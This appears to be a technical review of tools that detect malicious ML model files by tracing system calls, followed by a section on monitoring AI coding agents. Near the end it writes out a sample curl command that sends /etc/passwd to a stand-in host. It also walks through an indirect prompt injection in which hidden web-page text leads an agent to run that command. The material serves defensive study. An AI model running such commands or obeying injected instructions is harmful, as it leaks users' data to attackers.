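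*Malicious ML Model Detection by Learning Dynamic Behaviors* (Nambiar, Pradhan and Soremekun, 2026) includes a trace from another harmless model that ModelTracer flags. Python opens an IPv6 socket and binds it to `::1`, the machine's own address. Neither call contacts another computer, and the code is probably just checking whether IPv6 works.

Python normally imports a module only once per process. If one process loads two models that need the same library, the probe appears when the first model loads but not when the second does. What the process did earlier can therefore affect whether ModelTracer flags a harmless file.

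Estimates of ModelTracer's false alarms vary widely. Ali and Case report that 84% of the models flagged in the original study were harmless. Nambiar and colleagues ran ModelTracer on 2,025 popular text-generation models and got no false alarms. These figures don't directly contradict each other, because the first is a share of flagged models and the second is a share of harmless models.

A short list also misses attacks that use other calls. For example, malicious code needs only ordinary file operations to add the attacker's key to the user's `authorized_keys` file, which controls who may log in over SSH.

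### Learning from harmless models

Nambiar and colleagues trained their detector, DynaHug, only on harmless models, because Hugging Face has many of those and few known malicious ones. DynaHug does not check calls against a list of bad ones.

1. It downloads about 2,000 of the most-liked PyTorch models for one task, such as text generation.
2. It loads each model in a Docker container under strace.
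3. For each system call, it records whether the call occurred and how often, and scales the counts so that very common calls don't dominate.
4. It trains a one-class support vector machine, a classifier that draws a boundary around the harmless examples. A new model outside the boundary counts as malicious.

The classifier gives a new model *x* the score

s(x) = Σ αᵢ exp(−γ‖x − xᵢ‖²)

where each xᵢ is a training example, αᵢ is its learned weight and ‖x − xᵢ‖ is the distance between the two sets of scaled values. If the score is below a learned threshold, DynaHug flags the model. The project's page, *DynaHug*, gives γ = 0.1 for the main text-generation classifier.

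Nambiar and colleagues tested a separate classifier for each of three tasks:

| Task | Harmless models flagged | Real malicious models detected | Models with injected payloads detected |
|---|---|---|---|
| Text generation | 1 of 2,025 | 25 of 25 | 1,986 of 2,000 |
| Text classification | 28 of 2,004 | 4 of 4 | 1,985 of 2,000 |
| Feature extraction | 18 of 2,017 | 13 of 17 | 1,994 of 2,000 |

These are good results, but the last column is less varied than it looks. The researchers made each set of 2,000 files by inserting 84 payloads into harmless models, so each payload appears many times. They also used some malicious models to choose the classifier's settings, but not to train it.

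Counts of the system calls set_robust_list, clone and futex, which Linux programs use to create and coordinate threads and processes, contributed most to detection. In the test case, DynaHug would probably react to the extra calls that create the shell. But its output is a score, so an analyst would have to check the trace to learn that the shell ran curl.

Ali and Case later tested DynaHug on a different collection, the PickleBall dataset, with 252 harmless and 84 malicious files. It flagged all 336, so it did not distinguish the harmless files from the malicious ones.

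Ali and Case attribute the false alarms to training the classifier only on text-generation models, which made models for other tasks and libraries look abnormal. This is probably part of the explanation, but Nambiar and colleagues also trained a classifier on a mixture of tasks, and it flagged only 9 of 200 harmless models, compared with 4 of 200 for text generation alone. Differences between tasks may not be large enough to explain 252 false alarms out of 252.

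The test environment may also have affected the results. Nambiar and colleagues warn that strace's output varies with the software and hardware. For instance, a machine with more processor cores may start more threads, which changes the counts DynaHug relies on most.

Under this formula, a small change can greatly affect the score. Suppose a library update adds 20 calls of a kind whose count normally has a standard deviation of 2. After scaling, the difference is 10, so the exponential for every training example is at most about exp(−0.1 × 10²), or 0.00005, and every file scores almost zero, harmless or not. This would fit another of Ali and Case's observations, that DynaHug gave every file in a separate test the same confidence score, including a harmless one.

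A team using DynaHug would therefore have to train it in the environment where it will run, and probably retrain it after library updates.

### MOAT's allowlists

MOAT, the scanner that Digregorio and colleagues built, compares each thing a model does with a written list of "actions", meaning interactions with the host such as reading a file, opening a network connection or creating a process. An action includes its context, so the same system calls can correspond to different actions. For example, reading `model.pt` and reading `/etc/passwd` are different actions, and a clone call creates a thread or a process depending on its flags.

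MOAT reports every action that is not on its list of expected actions. The design assumes that no malicious action is on the list. This holds only if the list permits nothing that an attacker can use, so someone has to check each entry for possible misuse.

MOAT has a separate list for each framework and phase. Three of them, slightly simplified, permit the following:

| | PyTorch, loading | Keras, loading | TensorFlow, inference |
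|---|---|---|---|
| Reading files | Python's files and the model's folder | The same, plus the C library and a few system files | The same as Keras, with some different system files that describe the processor and memory |
| Changing files | PyTorch's temporary loading files | None | None |
| Executing files | None | uname and the C library | uname and the C library |
| Network connections | None | None | None |

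All three also allow the model to print text.

To build the lists, the researchers ran 600 harmless models they had generated and about 1,000 from Hugging Face. Whenever a new action appeared, an analyst worked out what had caused it and whether a malicious file could misuse it. If so, the entry had to be narrower, perhaps permitting one file instead of a whole directory. Each check took between 10 minutes and 3 hours.

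The five resulting lists have 4 to 21 entries each, with only 27 different entries among them. The researchers estimate that an experienced analyst could add a framework in one or two working days. They didn't have to change the lists between PyTorch 2.5.1 and 2.9.1, or between Keras 3.8 and 3.12, which suggests the lists may need little maintenance.

In the test case, MOAT would report a violation at the first of the four system calls, when Python creates process 4207, because PyTorch doesn't need a new process to load a model. If the file made Python read an SSH key instead, the path would be outside the permitted folders.

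For a monitor that covers only program starts, the lists also suggest that a PyTorch server can refuse every program start while it loads a model, and that a Keras server needs little more than uname. MOAT's Keras list includes uname in four directories, presumably because MOAT checks calls on entry, which includes the failed attempts of a PATH search. A monitor at sched_process_exec would need to list only the path that exists.

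### Marking the start and end of a phase

Importing a framework causes many file reads and other calls that have nothing to do with a particular model. MOAT's orchestrator, the part that runs the model, does this work in advance and then marks the phase with two signals. In outline:

```python
import os, signal, torch

os.kill(os.getpid(), signal.SIGUSR1)    # start tracing
model = torch.load("model.pt", weights_only=False)
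os.kill(os.getpid(), signal.SIGUSR2)    # stop tracing
```

The tracer intercepts the signals and checks only the system calls made between them. The orchestrator performs roughly 20 initialisation steps, including the imports that trigger the network probe, before the first signal, so MOAT doesn't flag `twitter-roberta-base-sentiment.bin`.

The process that runs the untrusted file also sends the stop signal, so malicious code could try to send the signal early and attack after tracing has stopped. Digregorio and colleagues don't claim that their implementation can withstand deliberate evasion.

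The tracer uses ptrace, compares each action with the list and logs any violation. Setting up the framework took 0.1 to 2.3 seconds, on top of the tracing overhead given earlier.

### What MOAT's tests measured

Digregorio and colleagues first tested MOAT on 31 proofs of concept, small programs or files that demonstrate an attack. Of these, 23 exploited eight published flaws in Keras and PyTorch, four abused ordinary TensorFlow functions, and four used a Keras weakness that was not yet public. The researchers used vulnerable versions or switched off protections where necessary. MOAT detected all 31, although its lists contained nothing specific to any of the flaws.

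The 31 files are variations on four attacks, some of them only partly implemented:

- writing a Python file that replaces a commonly used library
- sending a private file, such as an SSH key, to the attacker
- contacting the attacker's server to reveal the victim's IP address
- adding the attacker's key to `authorized_keys` and sending the username to the attacker

None of these requires the model to start another program, so a monitor like the bpftrace script could miss all four. The test is good evidence that MOAT doesn't depend on how an attack gets into a file, but weaker evidence about attacks with other aims, because it covered only four.

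The researchers then collected 88,789 PyTorch and Keras files from Hugging Face repositories updated in 2025. They excluded files that needed extra libraries, which left 77,974, and tested only the loading phase. MOAT flagged 23 files, and the researchers inspected them all and confirmed that they were malicious, with behaviour ranging from running commands to opening reverse shells.

MOAT raised no false alarms on about 78,000 files, which is strong evidence that it causes few. If we treat the files as a random sample, this result suggests a true rate below roughly 1 in 26,000, compared with the 1 in 1,000 assumed in the earlier example of alert overload.

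MOAT caught 23 malicious files, but we don't know how many it missed, because nobody inspected the 77,951 files it passed. The reported result would be the same whether it missed 2, for a detection rate of 92%, or 77, for a rate of 23%.

A test of this design probably misses some malicious files. A file whose malicious code runs only during inference would look harmless while it loads. An attacker could also make a file depend on an unusual library, which would have put it among the 10,815 files the researchers excluded.

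Running other scanners on the same files and inspecting whatever they flag would give only a partial estimate of m, because it would leave out attacks that every scanner misses. Ali and Case did this with 10,000 models and found three malicious ones that their own system, ModelShield, had missed.

### Is a file that prints a message malicious?

A test on files with known labels can measure missed attacks directly if the labels are correct. Kellas and colleagues assembled the PickleBall dataset to test their own defence, which examines a library's source code and blocks any function that its models shouldn't need. Other researchers have since reused the dataset, and they disagree about which files are malicious.

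The repository has 253 harmless files, one more than the paper reports, and 84 malicious ones. Digregorio and colleagues removed three of the malicious files because they attack only Windows. They relabelled `twitter-roberta-base-sentiment.bin` as harmless because it has no payload, a conclusion Ali and Case reached independently. That left 254 harmless files and 80 malicious ones.

The real dispute concerns 21 of those 80:

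| Files | What happens when the file loads |
|---|---|
| 18 | It uses `eval` to print a message, or does something similar |
| 1 | It fails with a syntax error before the payload runs |
| 1 | It compiles malicious code but never runs it |
| 1 | It tries to run a script that isn't in the dataset |

Digregorio and colleagues consider these harmless, because none of them affects the host. MOAT passes all 21, so it misses none of the malicious files under the new labels and 21 of 80, or 26%, under the old ones. The relabelling changes the results for other tools too:

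| Tool | Harmless files flagged, old labels | Malicious files missed, old labels | Harmless files flagged, new labels | Malicious files missed, new labels |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| MOAT | 0 of 254 | 21 of 80 | 0 of 275 | 0 of 59 |
| ModelTracer | 1 of 254 | 38 of 80 | 1 of 275 | 17 of 59 |
| Kellas and colleagues' defence | 52 of 254 | 0 of 80 | 73 of 275 | 0 of 59 |
| PyTorch's weights_only | 96 of 254 | 0 of 80 | 117 of 275 | 0 of 59 |

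The last two tools restrict which functions a file may use, so they block `eval` whatever it does. Under the new labels, 21 of their correct decisions become false alarms. The comparison also puts weights_only at a disadvantage, because it is meant to load weights and many of the harmless files contain more than weights.

Caution is warranted when a tool's developers relabel exactly the files their tool misses, but their argument is reasonable. A behaviour monitor can't detect harm that never happens, and a server that prints "hello" hasn't been compromised. The counterargument is that a model has no good reason to carry an `eval` payload. The payload's author has shown that the file can run code, and could replace the message with a real command in seconds.

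The right label depends on the decision. An operator deciding whether to shut down a server needs to know whether the file did any damage, so the new labels are more useful. A model-sharing site deciding whether to host the file should probably reject it, and the old labels suit that decision better.

Even the definition of harmless behaviour is unsettled. Ali and Case put four files that write text files with names such as `YOUAREHACKED.txt` in the same category as files that only print. MOAT appears to have flagged these four, because it permits a model to print but not to write files to arbitrary locations.

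### Running the allowlists on eBPF

Digregorio and colleagues say a live monitor could keep the same overall approach while using a faster mechanism than ptrace, such as eBPF, though several details would have to change.

The eBPF program should check system calls against the allowlist inside the kernel. Nearly all the calls in a model load are expected, so sending only violations to user space keeps the buffer almost empty.

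File paths need more care because a malicious download could include a symbolic link in the model's folder that points to the user's SSH key. A check of the path as Python gave it would pass, because the link is in a permitted folder. An LSM hook that runs when the kernel opens a file can check the file that the link leads to, and can also block access to it.

The signals should determine which allowlist applies, rather than turn monitoring on and off. If malicious code then signalled the end of loading too early, the only additional actions open to it would be those on the inference list that aren't on the loading list. Neither list should permit a shell or an outside connection.

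A live server also needs more allowlist entries than a scanner because it writes logs, uses a GPU and may run a compiler for `torch.compile`. Some entries would differ between machines, since MOAT's lists include an x86-specific path for the C library.

Network access is the hardest behaviour to allowlist, because a server has to accept requests and may fetch models from storage. An allowlist that permits those connections for the whole process also permits them for malicious code running in it. The operator can avoid this by loading and running the model in a separate process that has no network access and receives its inputs from the server through a local channel.

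Many servers, however, handle both loading and inference in one process, and may load one model while another serves requests. Two threads can then be in different phases at the same time, so a single phase setting for the process would apply the wrong allowlist to one of them. The monitor has to match each system call to the model operation that caused it.

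## Tracing system calls back to the model that caused them

Suppose thread 4111 of the model server is loading a new model file while thread 4112 answers requests with a model that has run safely for weeks. The server then opens a connection to an unfamiliar address. The operator needs to know which model to remove, but can't tell from the process ID because both threads belong to process 4100.

Attributing a system call to the model operation that caused it is hard even when a process handles one model at a time. The thousands of system calls during a `torch.load` come from PyTorch, the GPU's software, other Python packages, the dynamic linker (which loads shared libraries) and any code in the model file. The kernel receives a system call number and some arguments in every case, so the calls look alike. MOAT's signals show when a phase starts and ends but don't separate the model's calls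 from the framework's.

ModelShield, the scanner that Ali and Case built, puts a label on each thread instead.

### Labelling a thread

ModelShield replaces the framework functions that load or run a model with wrappers, which do some extra work and then call the original function. A simplified wrapper for `torch.load` might look like this:

```python
def labelled_load(path):
    thread = threading.get_native_id()
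    previous = labels.get(thread)
    labels[thread] = (new_id(), "loading")
    try:
        return original_load(path)
    finally:
        labels[thread] = previous
```

`labels` stands for a BPF map that both the wrapper and the eBPF programs can use. The wrapper restores the previous label at the end because one loading function often calls another.

If the test file from earlier loads on thread 4111, the label travels as follows:

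1. The wrapper stores the identifier A17 and the phase "loading" under 4111.
2. The thread opens the model file. An eBPF program at the system-call tracepoint looks up 4111 in the map and adds A17 to its record.
3. `os.system` creates process 4207. A probe on clone copies the label from 4111 to 4207.
4. Process 4207 becomes sh and creates 4208, which gets the label in the same way and becomes curl.

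Thread 4112 has a different label, so the operator can tell that the new file caused the connection. A monitor could also apply the loading allowlist to one thread and the inference allowlist to the other.

Inference methods differ between models, so when a load finishes, ModelShield examines the returned object and wraps the callable methods it finds, such as `generate`. Thread pools reuse their threads, so a worker could still carry the label of an earlier task. To prevent this, ModelShield intercepts the function that submits work to the pool and sets the worker's label before each task begins.

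### Calls that arrive without a label

ModelShield makes the copy in step 3 when clone returns, which can be too late. Dileo found the same timing problem in other tracers.

ModelShield sends an unlabelled call to user space, where another program tries to find its origin. That program checks the list of thread-pool tasks, then the stored links between parents and children, then a table that the Python wrappers keep. If none of these reveals the origin, the program assigns the call to the model under analysis.

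That last step is reasonable in a scanner that runs one model at a time. On a server with several models it would be a guess, so a live monitor should mark the call as unassigned. The monitor should also copy labels at `sched_process_fork` so that fewer calls need repair.

### What a label doesn't show

A label identifies the call to `torch.load`, but not the code inside it that made the system call. If a load makes Python import a library that opens a socket, that socket gets the same label as one opened by malicious code.

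One of Ali and Case's tests shows the effect. In *My model is malware to you*, Zhu, Chen and colleagues (2025) devised the four TensorFlow attacks that MOAT's tests also used. When Ali and Case ran the attack that reveals the victim's IP address, ModelShield correctly reported the connection. It also reported theft of hardware information, because the process had read `/proc/cpuinfo` before connecting. Machine-learning frameworks read that file to find out what the processor can do, so the report of theft was probably wrong.

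The wrapper is also a weak point if an attacker knows about it. It runs in the same Python process as the untrusted file, and that process has to be able to change labels, so malicious code in the file could try to delete its own label or take another model's. Ali and Case assume that the attacker starts without root access, but code already running inside a privileged Python process might not need any further access to change a label.

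Running each model in its own process is simpler and safer for a live server. The operator can then use the process ancestry to see which model caused a program start, without relying on any code in the untrusted process. Labels are useful when models must share a process or when the operator also wants to know the phase.

### Patterns with several steps

After attribution, ModelShield compares the calls from each phase with 195 patterns of malicious behaviour. A pattern is an ordered list of steps. For the theft of an SSH key over a TCP connection, the steps are:

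1. Open the key file for reading.
2. Read from it.
3. Connect to an outside address.
4. Send data.

Other calls may come between the calls in a pattern. ModelShield reads the events once and keeps track of its current position in every pattern, so the work grows with the number of events multiplied by the number of patterns. Classifying a model took a quarter of a second on average.

Checking only the order of the steps would cause false alarms. A harmless program might read `/etc/hosts` to look up an address and then connect to a server to download weights, which resembles reading a system file and sending it elsewhere. ModelShield therefore counts the read in step 2 only if it uses the path from step 1, and the send in step 4 only if it uses the socket from step 3.

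ModelShield also compares the number of bytes read with the number sent, allowing for encoding. Base64, which writes data as text, makes it about a third larger, so a 2,600-byte key becomes about 3,470 bytes. A 300-byte request for model weights wouldn't match. An attacker could try to hide the match by padding the key or sending it in small pieces, but ModelShield has other patterns for suspicious outbound connections.

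Some attacks repeat the same few steps many times. Ransomware, for example, opens, reads and overwrites one file after another. ModelShield looks for such cycles separately, because a fixed list of steps can't describe an attack of unknown length.

The patterns form a denylist of behaviour. Ali and Case looked for gaps in it by giving the language model GPT-5.5 the system calls of 10,000 models that ModelShield had passed. GPT-5.5 found one model that ran `touch`, a program that creates an empty file or updates a file's timestamp. They confirmed this by hand and added a pattern. An allowlist of program starts would have reported that model without a new pattern. GPT-5.5 also raised false alarms, including a high-confidence one caused by routine directory checks, so a person still has to review what it flags.

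### A reverse shell on Hugging Face

On 27 March 2026, someone uploaded a file to a Hugging Face repository that supposedly contained a Qwen2 language model. *Reverse Shell Malware Disguised as Qwen2 Model on Hugging Face* (2026), an advisory about the file, estimates that the real model would need about 300 MB. The file was 10.2 KB and contained a pickle instruction to open a reverse shell.

The uploader had packaged it in an old PyTorch format based on TAR archives. PyTorch can still load this format, but the site's scanners couldn't read it properly. When Ali and Case found the file three days later, each scanner had either reported no problem or not finished. The site had counted 108 downloads by then, though a download doesn't mean anyone loaded the file. Hugging Face removed the repository after their report.

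ModelShield's trace covers four processes:

| Process | Name | Main events |
|---|---|---|
| 132227 | python3.9 | Reads the model file, unpacks the archive, reads the malicious instruction and creates a child |
| 132228 | Probably sh | Loads the C library and creates a child |
| 132229 | sh, then bash | Starts bash and creates a child |
| 132230 | bash | Opens a socket, tries to connect to the attacker's server and writes two error messages |

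The link from the last process to the model depends on the monitor catching all three clone calls.

The two error messages were 34 and 56 bytes long, exactly the lengths of the messages that bash prints when a server refuses a connection to this address and port. The attacker's server was therefore probably not listening when the researchers ran the file. The attack failed at that point, but both shells had already started, so a monitor of program starts would still have raised an alert.

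Ali and Case count only one execve in this trace, for `bash`. An earlier execve must have started `sh`, because process 132229 was already named `sh` before it became `bash`. Process 132228 also loaded the C library, as a program does just after it starts. The published trace may leave out the `sh` call, or ModelShield may have missed it because, with `os.system`, clone returns too late for it to catch the call.

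The same gap could explain why ModelShield initially passed the model that ran `touch`. That model also used a function that starts a shell, and ModelShield has a pattern for that. Ali and Case don't discuss this possibility. An operator who builds a similar monitor should test it with `os.system` and check that the record for `sh` arrives.

### Few false alarms, many missed files

Ali and Case ran ModelShield and several other tools on the PickleBall dataset, using its original labels. In the table, recall is the share of malicious files that a tool detected.

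| Tool | Malicious files detected, of 84 | Harmless files flagged, of 252 | Recall | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ModelShield | 47 | 0 | 56% | 100% |
| ModelScan | 75 | 16 | 89% | 82% |
| PickleScan | 79 | 16 | 94% | 83% |
| ModelAudit | 82 | 91 | 98% | 47% |
| Kellas and colleagues' defence | 84 | 51 | 100% | 62% |

ModelScan, PickleScan and ModelAudit are static scanners. A fourth, Fickling, detected only 2 malicious files and flagged all 252 harmless ones. When Digregorio and colleagues tested a slightly older version, it detected every malicious file and flagged 96 of 254 harmless ones. Fickling can also check a file as it loads, and they may have used it that way. A scanner's results can depend heavily on how someone runs it.

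ModelShield missed 37 malicious files, for these reasons:

| Cause | Files |
|---|---|
| The payload ran but did nothing that ModelShield counts as harmful, such as printing a message | 23 |
| The test machine lacked a package that the payload needed | 5 |
| The payload was for Windows | 4 |
| The payload failed because of an error or a missing file | 4 |
| The file had no payload | 1 |

Installing the missing packages let ModelShield detect those five files too, bringing the total to 52. Ali and Case stress that ModelShield reported every malicious pattern it recorded. This helps in judging the classifier, but an operator also needs to know what else can cause a missed detection. A payload that fails on the scanning machine because a package is missing may work on a production server that has it.

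Finding no false alarms among 252 files is also compatible with a true rate of up to about 1.2%, which would mean over 1,700 false alarms in 145,000 models. The researchers' larger scan gives better evidence. ModelShield found 41 malicious models among 145,000 uploaded to three sites between 25 March and 5 May 2026. Ali and Case's *The Model Is the Malware*, a conference poster on an earlier version, reports that they confirmed every detection by hand. If no other file raised an alert, the false alarm rate is probably below 1 in 48,000.

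All 41 malicious models were among the 105,000 from Hugging Face. At the same rate, the 40,000 from ModelScope and Kaggle would have contained about 16, so malicious uploads seem to be more common on Hugging Face. GPT-5.5 found one of the 41, the model that ran `touch`, after ModelShield's patterns had missed it.

ModelAudit detected 38 of the 41 files, Fickling 33, PickleScan 23 and ModelScan 12. ModelShield's score of 41 isn't comparable, because the list contains only files that Ali and Case found with ModelShield.

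Running all four static scanners on 10,000 of the models gave a fairer comparison. At least one scanner flagged 565 of the models, and manual inspection confirmed 8 as malicious. ModelShield had detected 5 of the 8. Of the three it missed, two crashed the framework before their payload ran, and one read a sensitive file but did nothing with it. With only eight files, a true detection rate anywhere from about 24% to 91% would fit this result. The comparison also leaves out any attack that all the tools missed.

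The 557 false alarms show that the precision figures in the first table are a poor guide to precision on a model-sharing site. A quarter of the files in the PickleBall dataset are malicious, compared with fewer than one in a thousand here. Inspecting 557 harmless files at ten minutes each would take about 93 hours. ModelShield avoids that work but misses some of the malicious files. Ali and Case recommend using both kinds of tool. ModelShield can help rank the flagged files by urgency, but a clean result from it isn't a reason to clear a file that a static scanner has flagged.

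ModelShield took a median of 12.3 seconds per model, excluding the download, and finished 90% of models within 35.5 seconds. ModelScan's median was 2.3 seconds. One copy of ModelShield can process about 4,900 models a day, with limits of 5 GB per file and five minutes per model. That is fast enough to check new uploads, and a 12-second delay before deployment hardly matters.

The scan also used PyTorch 1.13.1 and 2.4.0, which were released before restricted loading became the default. Older versions make sense for a scanner because restricted loading would stop many payloads before they did anything. Users of newer versions with default settings would have been safe from some of the same files.

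### What a monitor of program starts would have recorded

ModelShield traces over a hundred system calls. The bpftrace script from earlier covers only program starts, so we can use Ali and Case's results to estimate what it would miss. Their appendix sorts the 41 models by behaviour:

| Behaviour | Models |
|---|---|
| Code execution only | 22 |
| Code execution and remote control, in one case with information theft | 7 |
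| Code execution and privilege escalation | 1 |
| Remote control only | 7 |
| System manipulation only | 4 |

Thirty models, or 73%, show code execution, which doesn't always involve starting a program. Five of the paper's six sample patterns for code execution include execve, and the sixth injects code into a running process. The appendix doesn't list the system calls for each model, so an exact count of the models that started a program isn't possible.

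The true figure could be somewhat lower than 30 because one of the models, judging by its name, uses PyTorch's function for starting worker processes. That would appear as Python starting another copy of Python, which many allowlists permit. The figure could also be higher, because a model outside the code-execution class may have started a program that no pattern covered, as the `touch` model originally did.

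The 11 models without code execution came from only four accounts, and all their names contain "bypass" or "poc" (proof of concept). Seven made a network connection, in most cases apparently through one of Python's standard modules for mail, news or file transfer. The other four changed files or wrote to the system log. Their creators were probably testing which Python functions the scanners had overlooked, rather than attacking anyone.

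The files that Ali and Case describe as real malware look different. *Malicious ML Model Report* (Ali, 2026) describes the second one from the main scan, which started a shell while it loaded, ran `id`, `whoami`, `hostname` and `cat` to identify the user and the machine, collected the environment variables, and made HTTPS connections to four outside addresses. A monitor of program starts would have recorded the shell and the commands, but not what data left the machine.

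By 19 August 2026, the researchers had scanned 224,164 models in a continued search of Hugging Face and found 105 more malicious models, two of which were real malware. One started shells as it loaded, and the other stole credentials and opened a reverse shell, so all four real samples used a shell.

Four cases are too few to establish a detection rate, but they support monitoring program starts first. They come from a period when attackers mainly had to get past file scanners. If this monitoring becomes common, attackers will have more reason to use methods that avoid it.

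### Attacks that start no program

*Deep Dive into the Abuse of DL APIs To Create Malicious* (Nabeel and Starov, 2025) argues that malware needs four basic abilities: reading files, writing files, sending data and receiving data. It identifies TensorFlow operations that provide each of these. For example, an operation that creates a dataset from a file can read a private file, and a debugging operation can send its contents to another machine.

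TensorFlow saves these operations as part of the model and runs them during inference inside the existing process, so no step requires execve. Static scanners also have difficulty detecting them because harmless models use the same operations. Zhu and colleagues found that Hugging Face, TensorFlow Hub and ModelScan detected none of their attacks of this kind. In Ali and Case's later test, ModelScan flagged two of the four, but it gave the same warnings about harmless models.

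ModelShield detected all four from their file and network activity. It also detected 25 other test files that used different functions or file formats to get past scanners. All 25 had the same basic payload, which accessed an SSH key, so this test shows that the delivery method makes little difference to ModelShield, but not how well it detects varied payloads.

Nabeel and Starov didn't find an operation that could start a program directly. In their second demonstration, the model downloads a malicious script and adds it to the user's shell profile, whose commands run when the user next logs in. The script then starts as a descendant of the login shell, so a monitor of the server's process tree misses it, just as it misses a cron job.

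The operator needs other events to detect such attacks:

| What the malicious model does | Program start below the server | Event that could reveal it |
|---|---|---|
| Reads an SSH key and sends it to the attacker | None | Opening the key file, then connecting to an outside address |
| Adds the attacker's key to `authorized_keys` | None | Opening that file for writing |
| Adds a command to the shell profile | None | Opening the profile for writing |
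| Contacts the attacker's server from Python | None | Connecting to an outside address |
| Receives Python code and runs it in the same process | None | Connecting to an outside address |

A monitor can cover these cases without recording every file access. A model server doesn't need to open an SSH key or change a shell profile, so a rule for a few sensitive paths should cause few false alarms. For outbound connections, the monitor needs a list of permitted destinations, such as the company's model storage. As with the allowlists, the eBPF program can make both checks in the kernel.

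### Payloads that haven't run

A malicious model may do harm only on a certain date, when a request contains a particular phrase, or on a machine with cloud credentials. Until then, its system calls are the same as a harmless model's.

ModelShield runs each model on an input of a suitable type, such as a random image or a sequence of text tokens, to try to trigger such code. This can expose a payload that runs on every request, but a random input is unlikely to trigger one that requires a secret phrase. A payload may also wait longer than the five minutes ModelShield allows.

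The results don't show how often attackers use such delays. Ali and Case put 22 of the 41 models in the loading phase and 19 in the execution phase, but not all of the 19 waited until someone used the model. They include the fake Qwen2 model, whose command ran while the file loaded. In that trace, the label changed from loading to execution when Python created the child process, so other models in this group may also have run their payloads during loading.

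Monitoring therefore has to continue after the scan, for as long as the model is in use. If the secret phrase arrives six months later and the model starts a shell, the production monitor can report it then. Until that happens, the payload can be found only by examining the file. A static scanner can sometimes find it, because the instruction is in the file whether or not it ever runs.

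## AI agents that start shells as part of their work

A shell on an inference server is worth an alert because the server has no reason to start one, but a coding agent starts shells routinely. The agent sends a user's request to a language model, carries out the action specified in the model's reply, sends back the result, and repeats this until the model returns a final answer. Many of the actions are commands, such as running a test or searching a folder, and the agent usually runs them in a shell. Operations agents, which manage servers, work similarly.

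In *AI coding agents are running on your machines*, Hernández and Lo Prete (2026) recorded the system calls of the coding agents Claude Code, Gemini CLI and Codex CLI. In one session, the agent started a new bash shell in each of five rounds within 10 seconds. The kernel reported 64 execve events, though the developer saw only one reply.

Claude Code runs on Bun and Gemini CLI on Node.js, which are both JavaScript runtimes, and Codex CLI is a compiled Rust program. Because none of them is a Python program, the bpftrace script from earlier would ignore them, apart from any Python programs they start. Adding `node` to the script would also match every other Node.js program on the machine. Sysdig's *Reference Library for Coding Agent Falco Threat Detection Rules* lists a field, `coding_agent.name`, that identifies the agent behind an event, so a rule can treat agents differently from other software.

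### How many alerts a shell rule would raise

*SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) covers almost 18,000 coding sessions from developers who had agreed to publish their logs. The agents made about 2 million tool calls (actions requested by the model). More than 45% of these calls were shell commands, or about 50 per session. Only 1.6% of the tool calls ran network programs such as curl, wget and ssh, or about 1.8 per session.

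If an organisation has 100 such sessions a day, a rule that reports every shell raises about 5,000 alerts a day. A rule for network programs alone still raises about 175. About 69% of the sample comes from Claude Code, so it isn't typical of all agents. The mix of commands also depends on the work. *Agentic AI Workload Characteristics* (2026) reports that curl made up about a quarter of the Bash commands from two models on GAIA, a benchmark of questions that often need web research.

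### Two process trees with the same shape

Suppose a user asks an agent to build a C project. The project needs a library, so the agent downloads it and runs make:

```
agent
└─ bash -c "curl -sO https://deps.example.com/lib.tar.gz && make; echo done"
   ├─ curl -sO https://deps.example.com/lib.tar.gz
   └─ make
```

In another session, the user makes the same request, but the agent looks up the build instructions on a web page. Hidden text on the page tells it to "register" the machine before building:

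```
agent
└─ bash -c "curl -sF f=@/etc/passwd https://check.example.net && make; echo done"
   ├─ curl -sF f=@/etc/passwd https://check.example.net
   └─ make
```

The second curl command sends the machine's list of user accounts to an unknown recipient. But both process trees contain the same programs with the same parents, so a rule that checks only program names and ancestry has to report both or neither.

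The arguments reveal this attack, but they might not have if the hidden text had told the agent to put the command in a script called `configure.sh`. Arguments can also be ambiguous. Uploading a build log is fine if the user asked for it, but it may be a leak if the agent is following instructions from a web page.

Security researchers call this attack indirect prompt injection. Hernández and Lo Prete explain that a language model receives the user's instructions and the text of a file or web page through the same channel, with no reliable separation between them. Even a comment in a source file can redirect the agent. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* describes reports from Google and the security company Forcepoint of injected instructions on live websites.

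A monitor can't distinguish the two sessions using the execve record alone, because the record doesn't include what the user asked for or what the agent read before it ran the command.

### AgentSight: matching commands to the model's replies

AgentSight (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) gets this information from the agent's conversation with its model. The agent normally encrypts that conversation with TLS, so a monitor on the network can't read it. But the agent passes plain text to a TLS library before encryption and receives plain text back after decryption. AgentSight attaches uprobes (probes on user-space functions) to the library's `SSL_write` and `SSL_read` functions.

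A second eBPF program records what the agent does to the machine. It uses the `sched_process_exec` tracepoint to build the process tree, and kprobes on system calls such as openat2, connect and execve. It filters events in the kernel, so user space receives only those from the agent and its descendants.

In the second session above, AgentSight would work roughly like this:

1. The agent sends the web page's text to the model. The probe on `SSL_write` copies it, including the hidden instruction.
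2. The model replies with the bash command. The reply arrives in pieces, which AgentSight copies at `SSL_read` and joins together.
3. A fraction of a second later, the agent starts bash, and the kernel probe reports the program start.
4. AgentSight links the shell to the reply using three clues: bash descends from the agent, it started within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds after the reply, and its arguments match text in the reply.
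5. It adds curl's file access and network connection to the same trace, then sends the trace to another language model, which Zheng and colleagues call the observer. The observer looks for actions that don't fit the task and returns an explanation with a confidence score.

The time window works well for short commands but less well for long ones. If make runs for two minutes, it may start hundreds of compilers long after the window closes. Ancestry still connects them to the agent, but the agent may have received many replies by then. *TraceLab* (2026) reports that 4.9% of Claude's tool calls took more than a minute. Agents can also delegate work to subagents, as happened in 48% of the Claude Code sessions that Baumann and colleagues collected. Two replies may then arrive almost together, so the text match has to separate them.

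Claude Code and Node.js contain their own copies of the TLS code, so a probe on the system's shared library would record nothing from them. According to eunomia-bpf's *AgentSight* documentation, the tool searches the agent's program file instead. The eBPF probes can't trace the Cursor editor, which mostly runs on macOS or Windows and sends its messages in a different format.

Zheng and colleagues tried AgentSight on three cases:

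- **A prompt injection.** They asked an agent to clone and build a C project whose README led to a web page with a hidden instruction. The agent read `/etc/passwd` and sent it to a collection server. AgentSight merged 521 events into 37, and the observer flagged the attack with high confidence.
- **A loop.** A research agent kept calling a search tool with the wrong arguments. The observer identified the repeated error as the cause.
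- **A team of six agents.** AgentSight recorded 3,153 events after merging and showed that some agents were waiting for files that others had locked.

The injection case shows that the method can work, but it is only one attack, and the paper doesn't report how often the observer flags harmless sessions.

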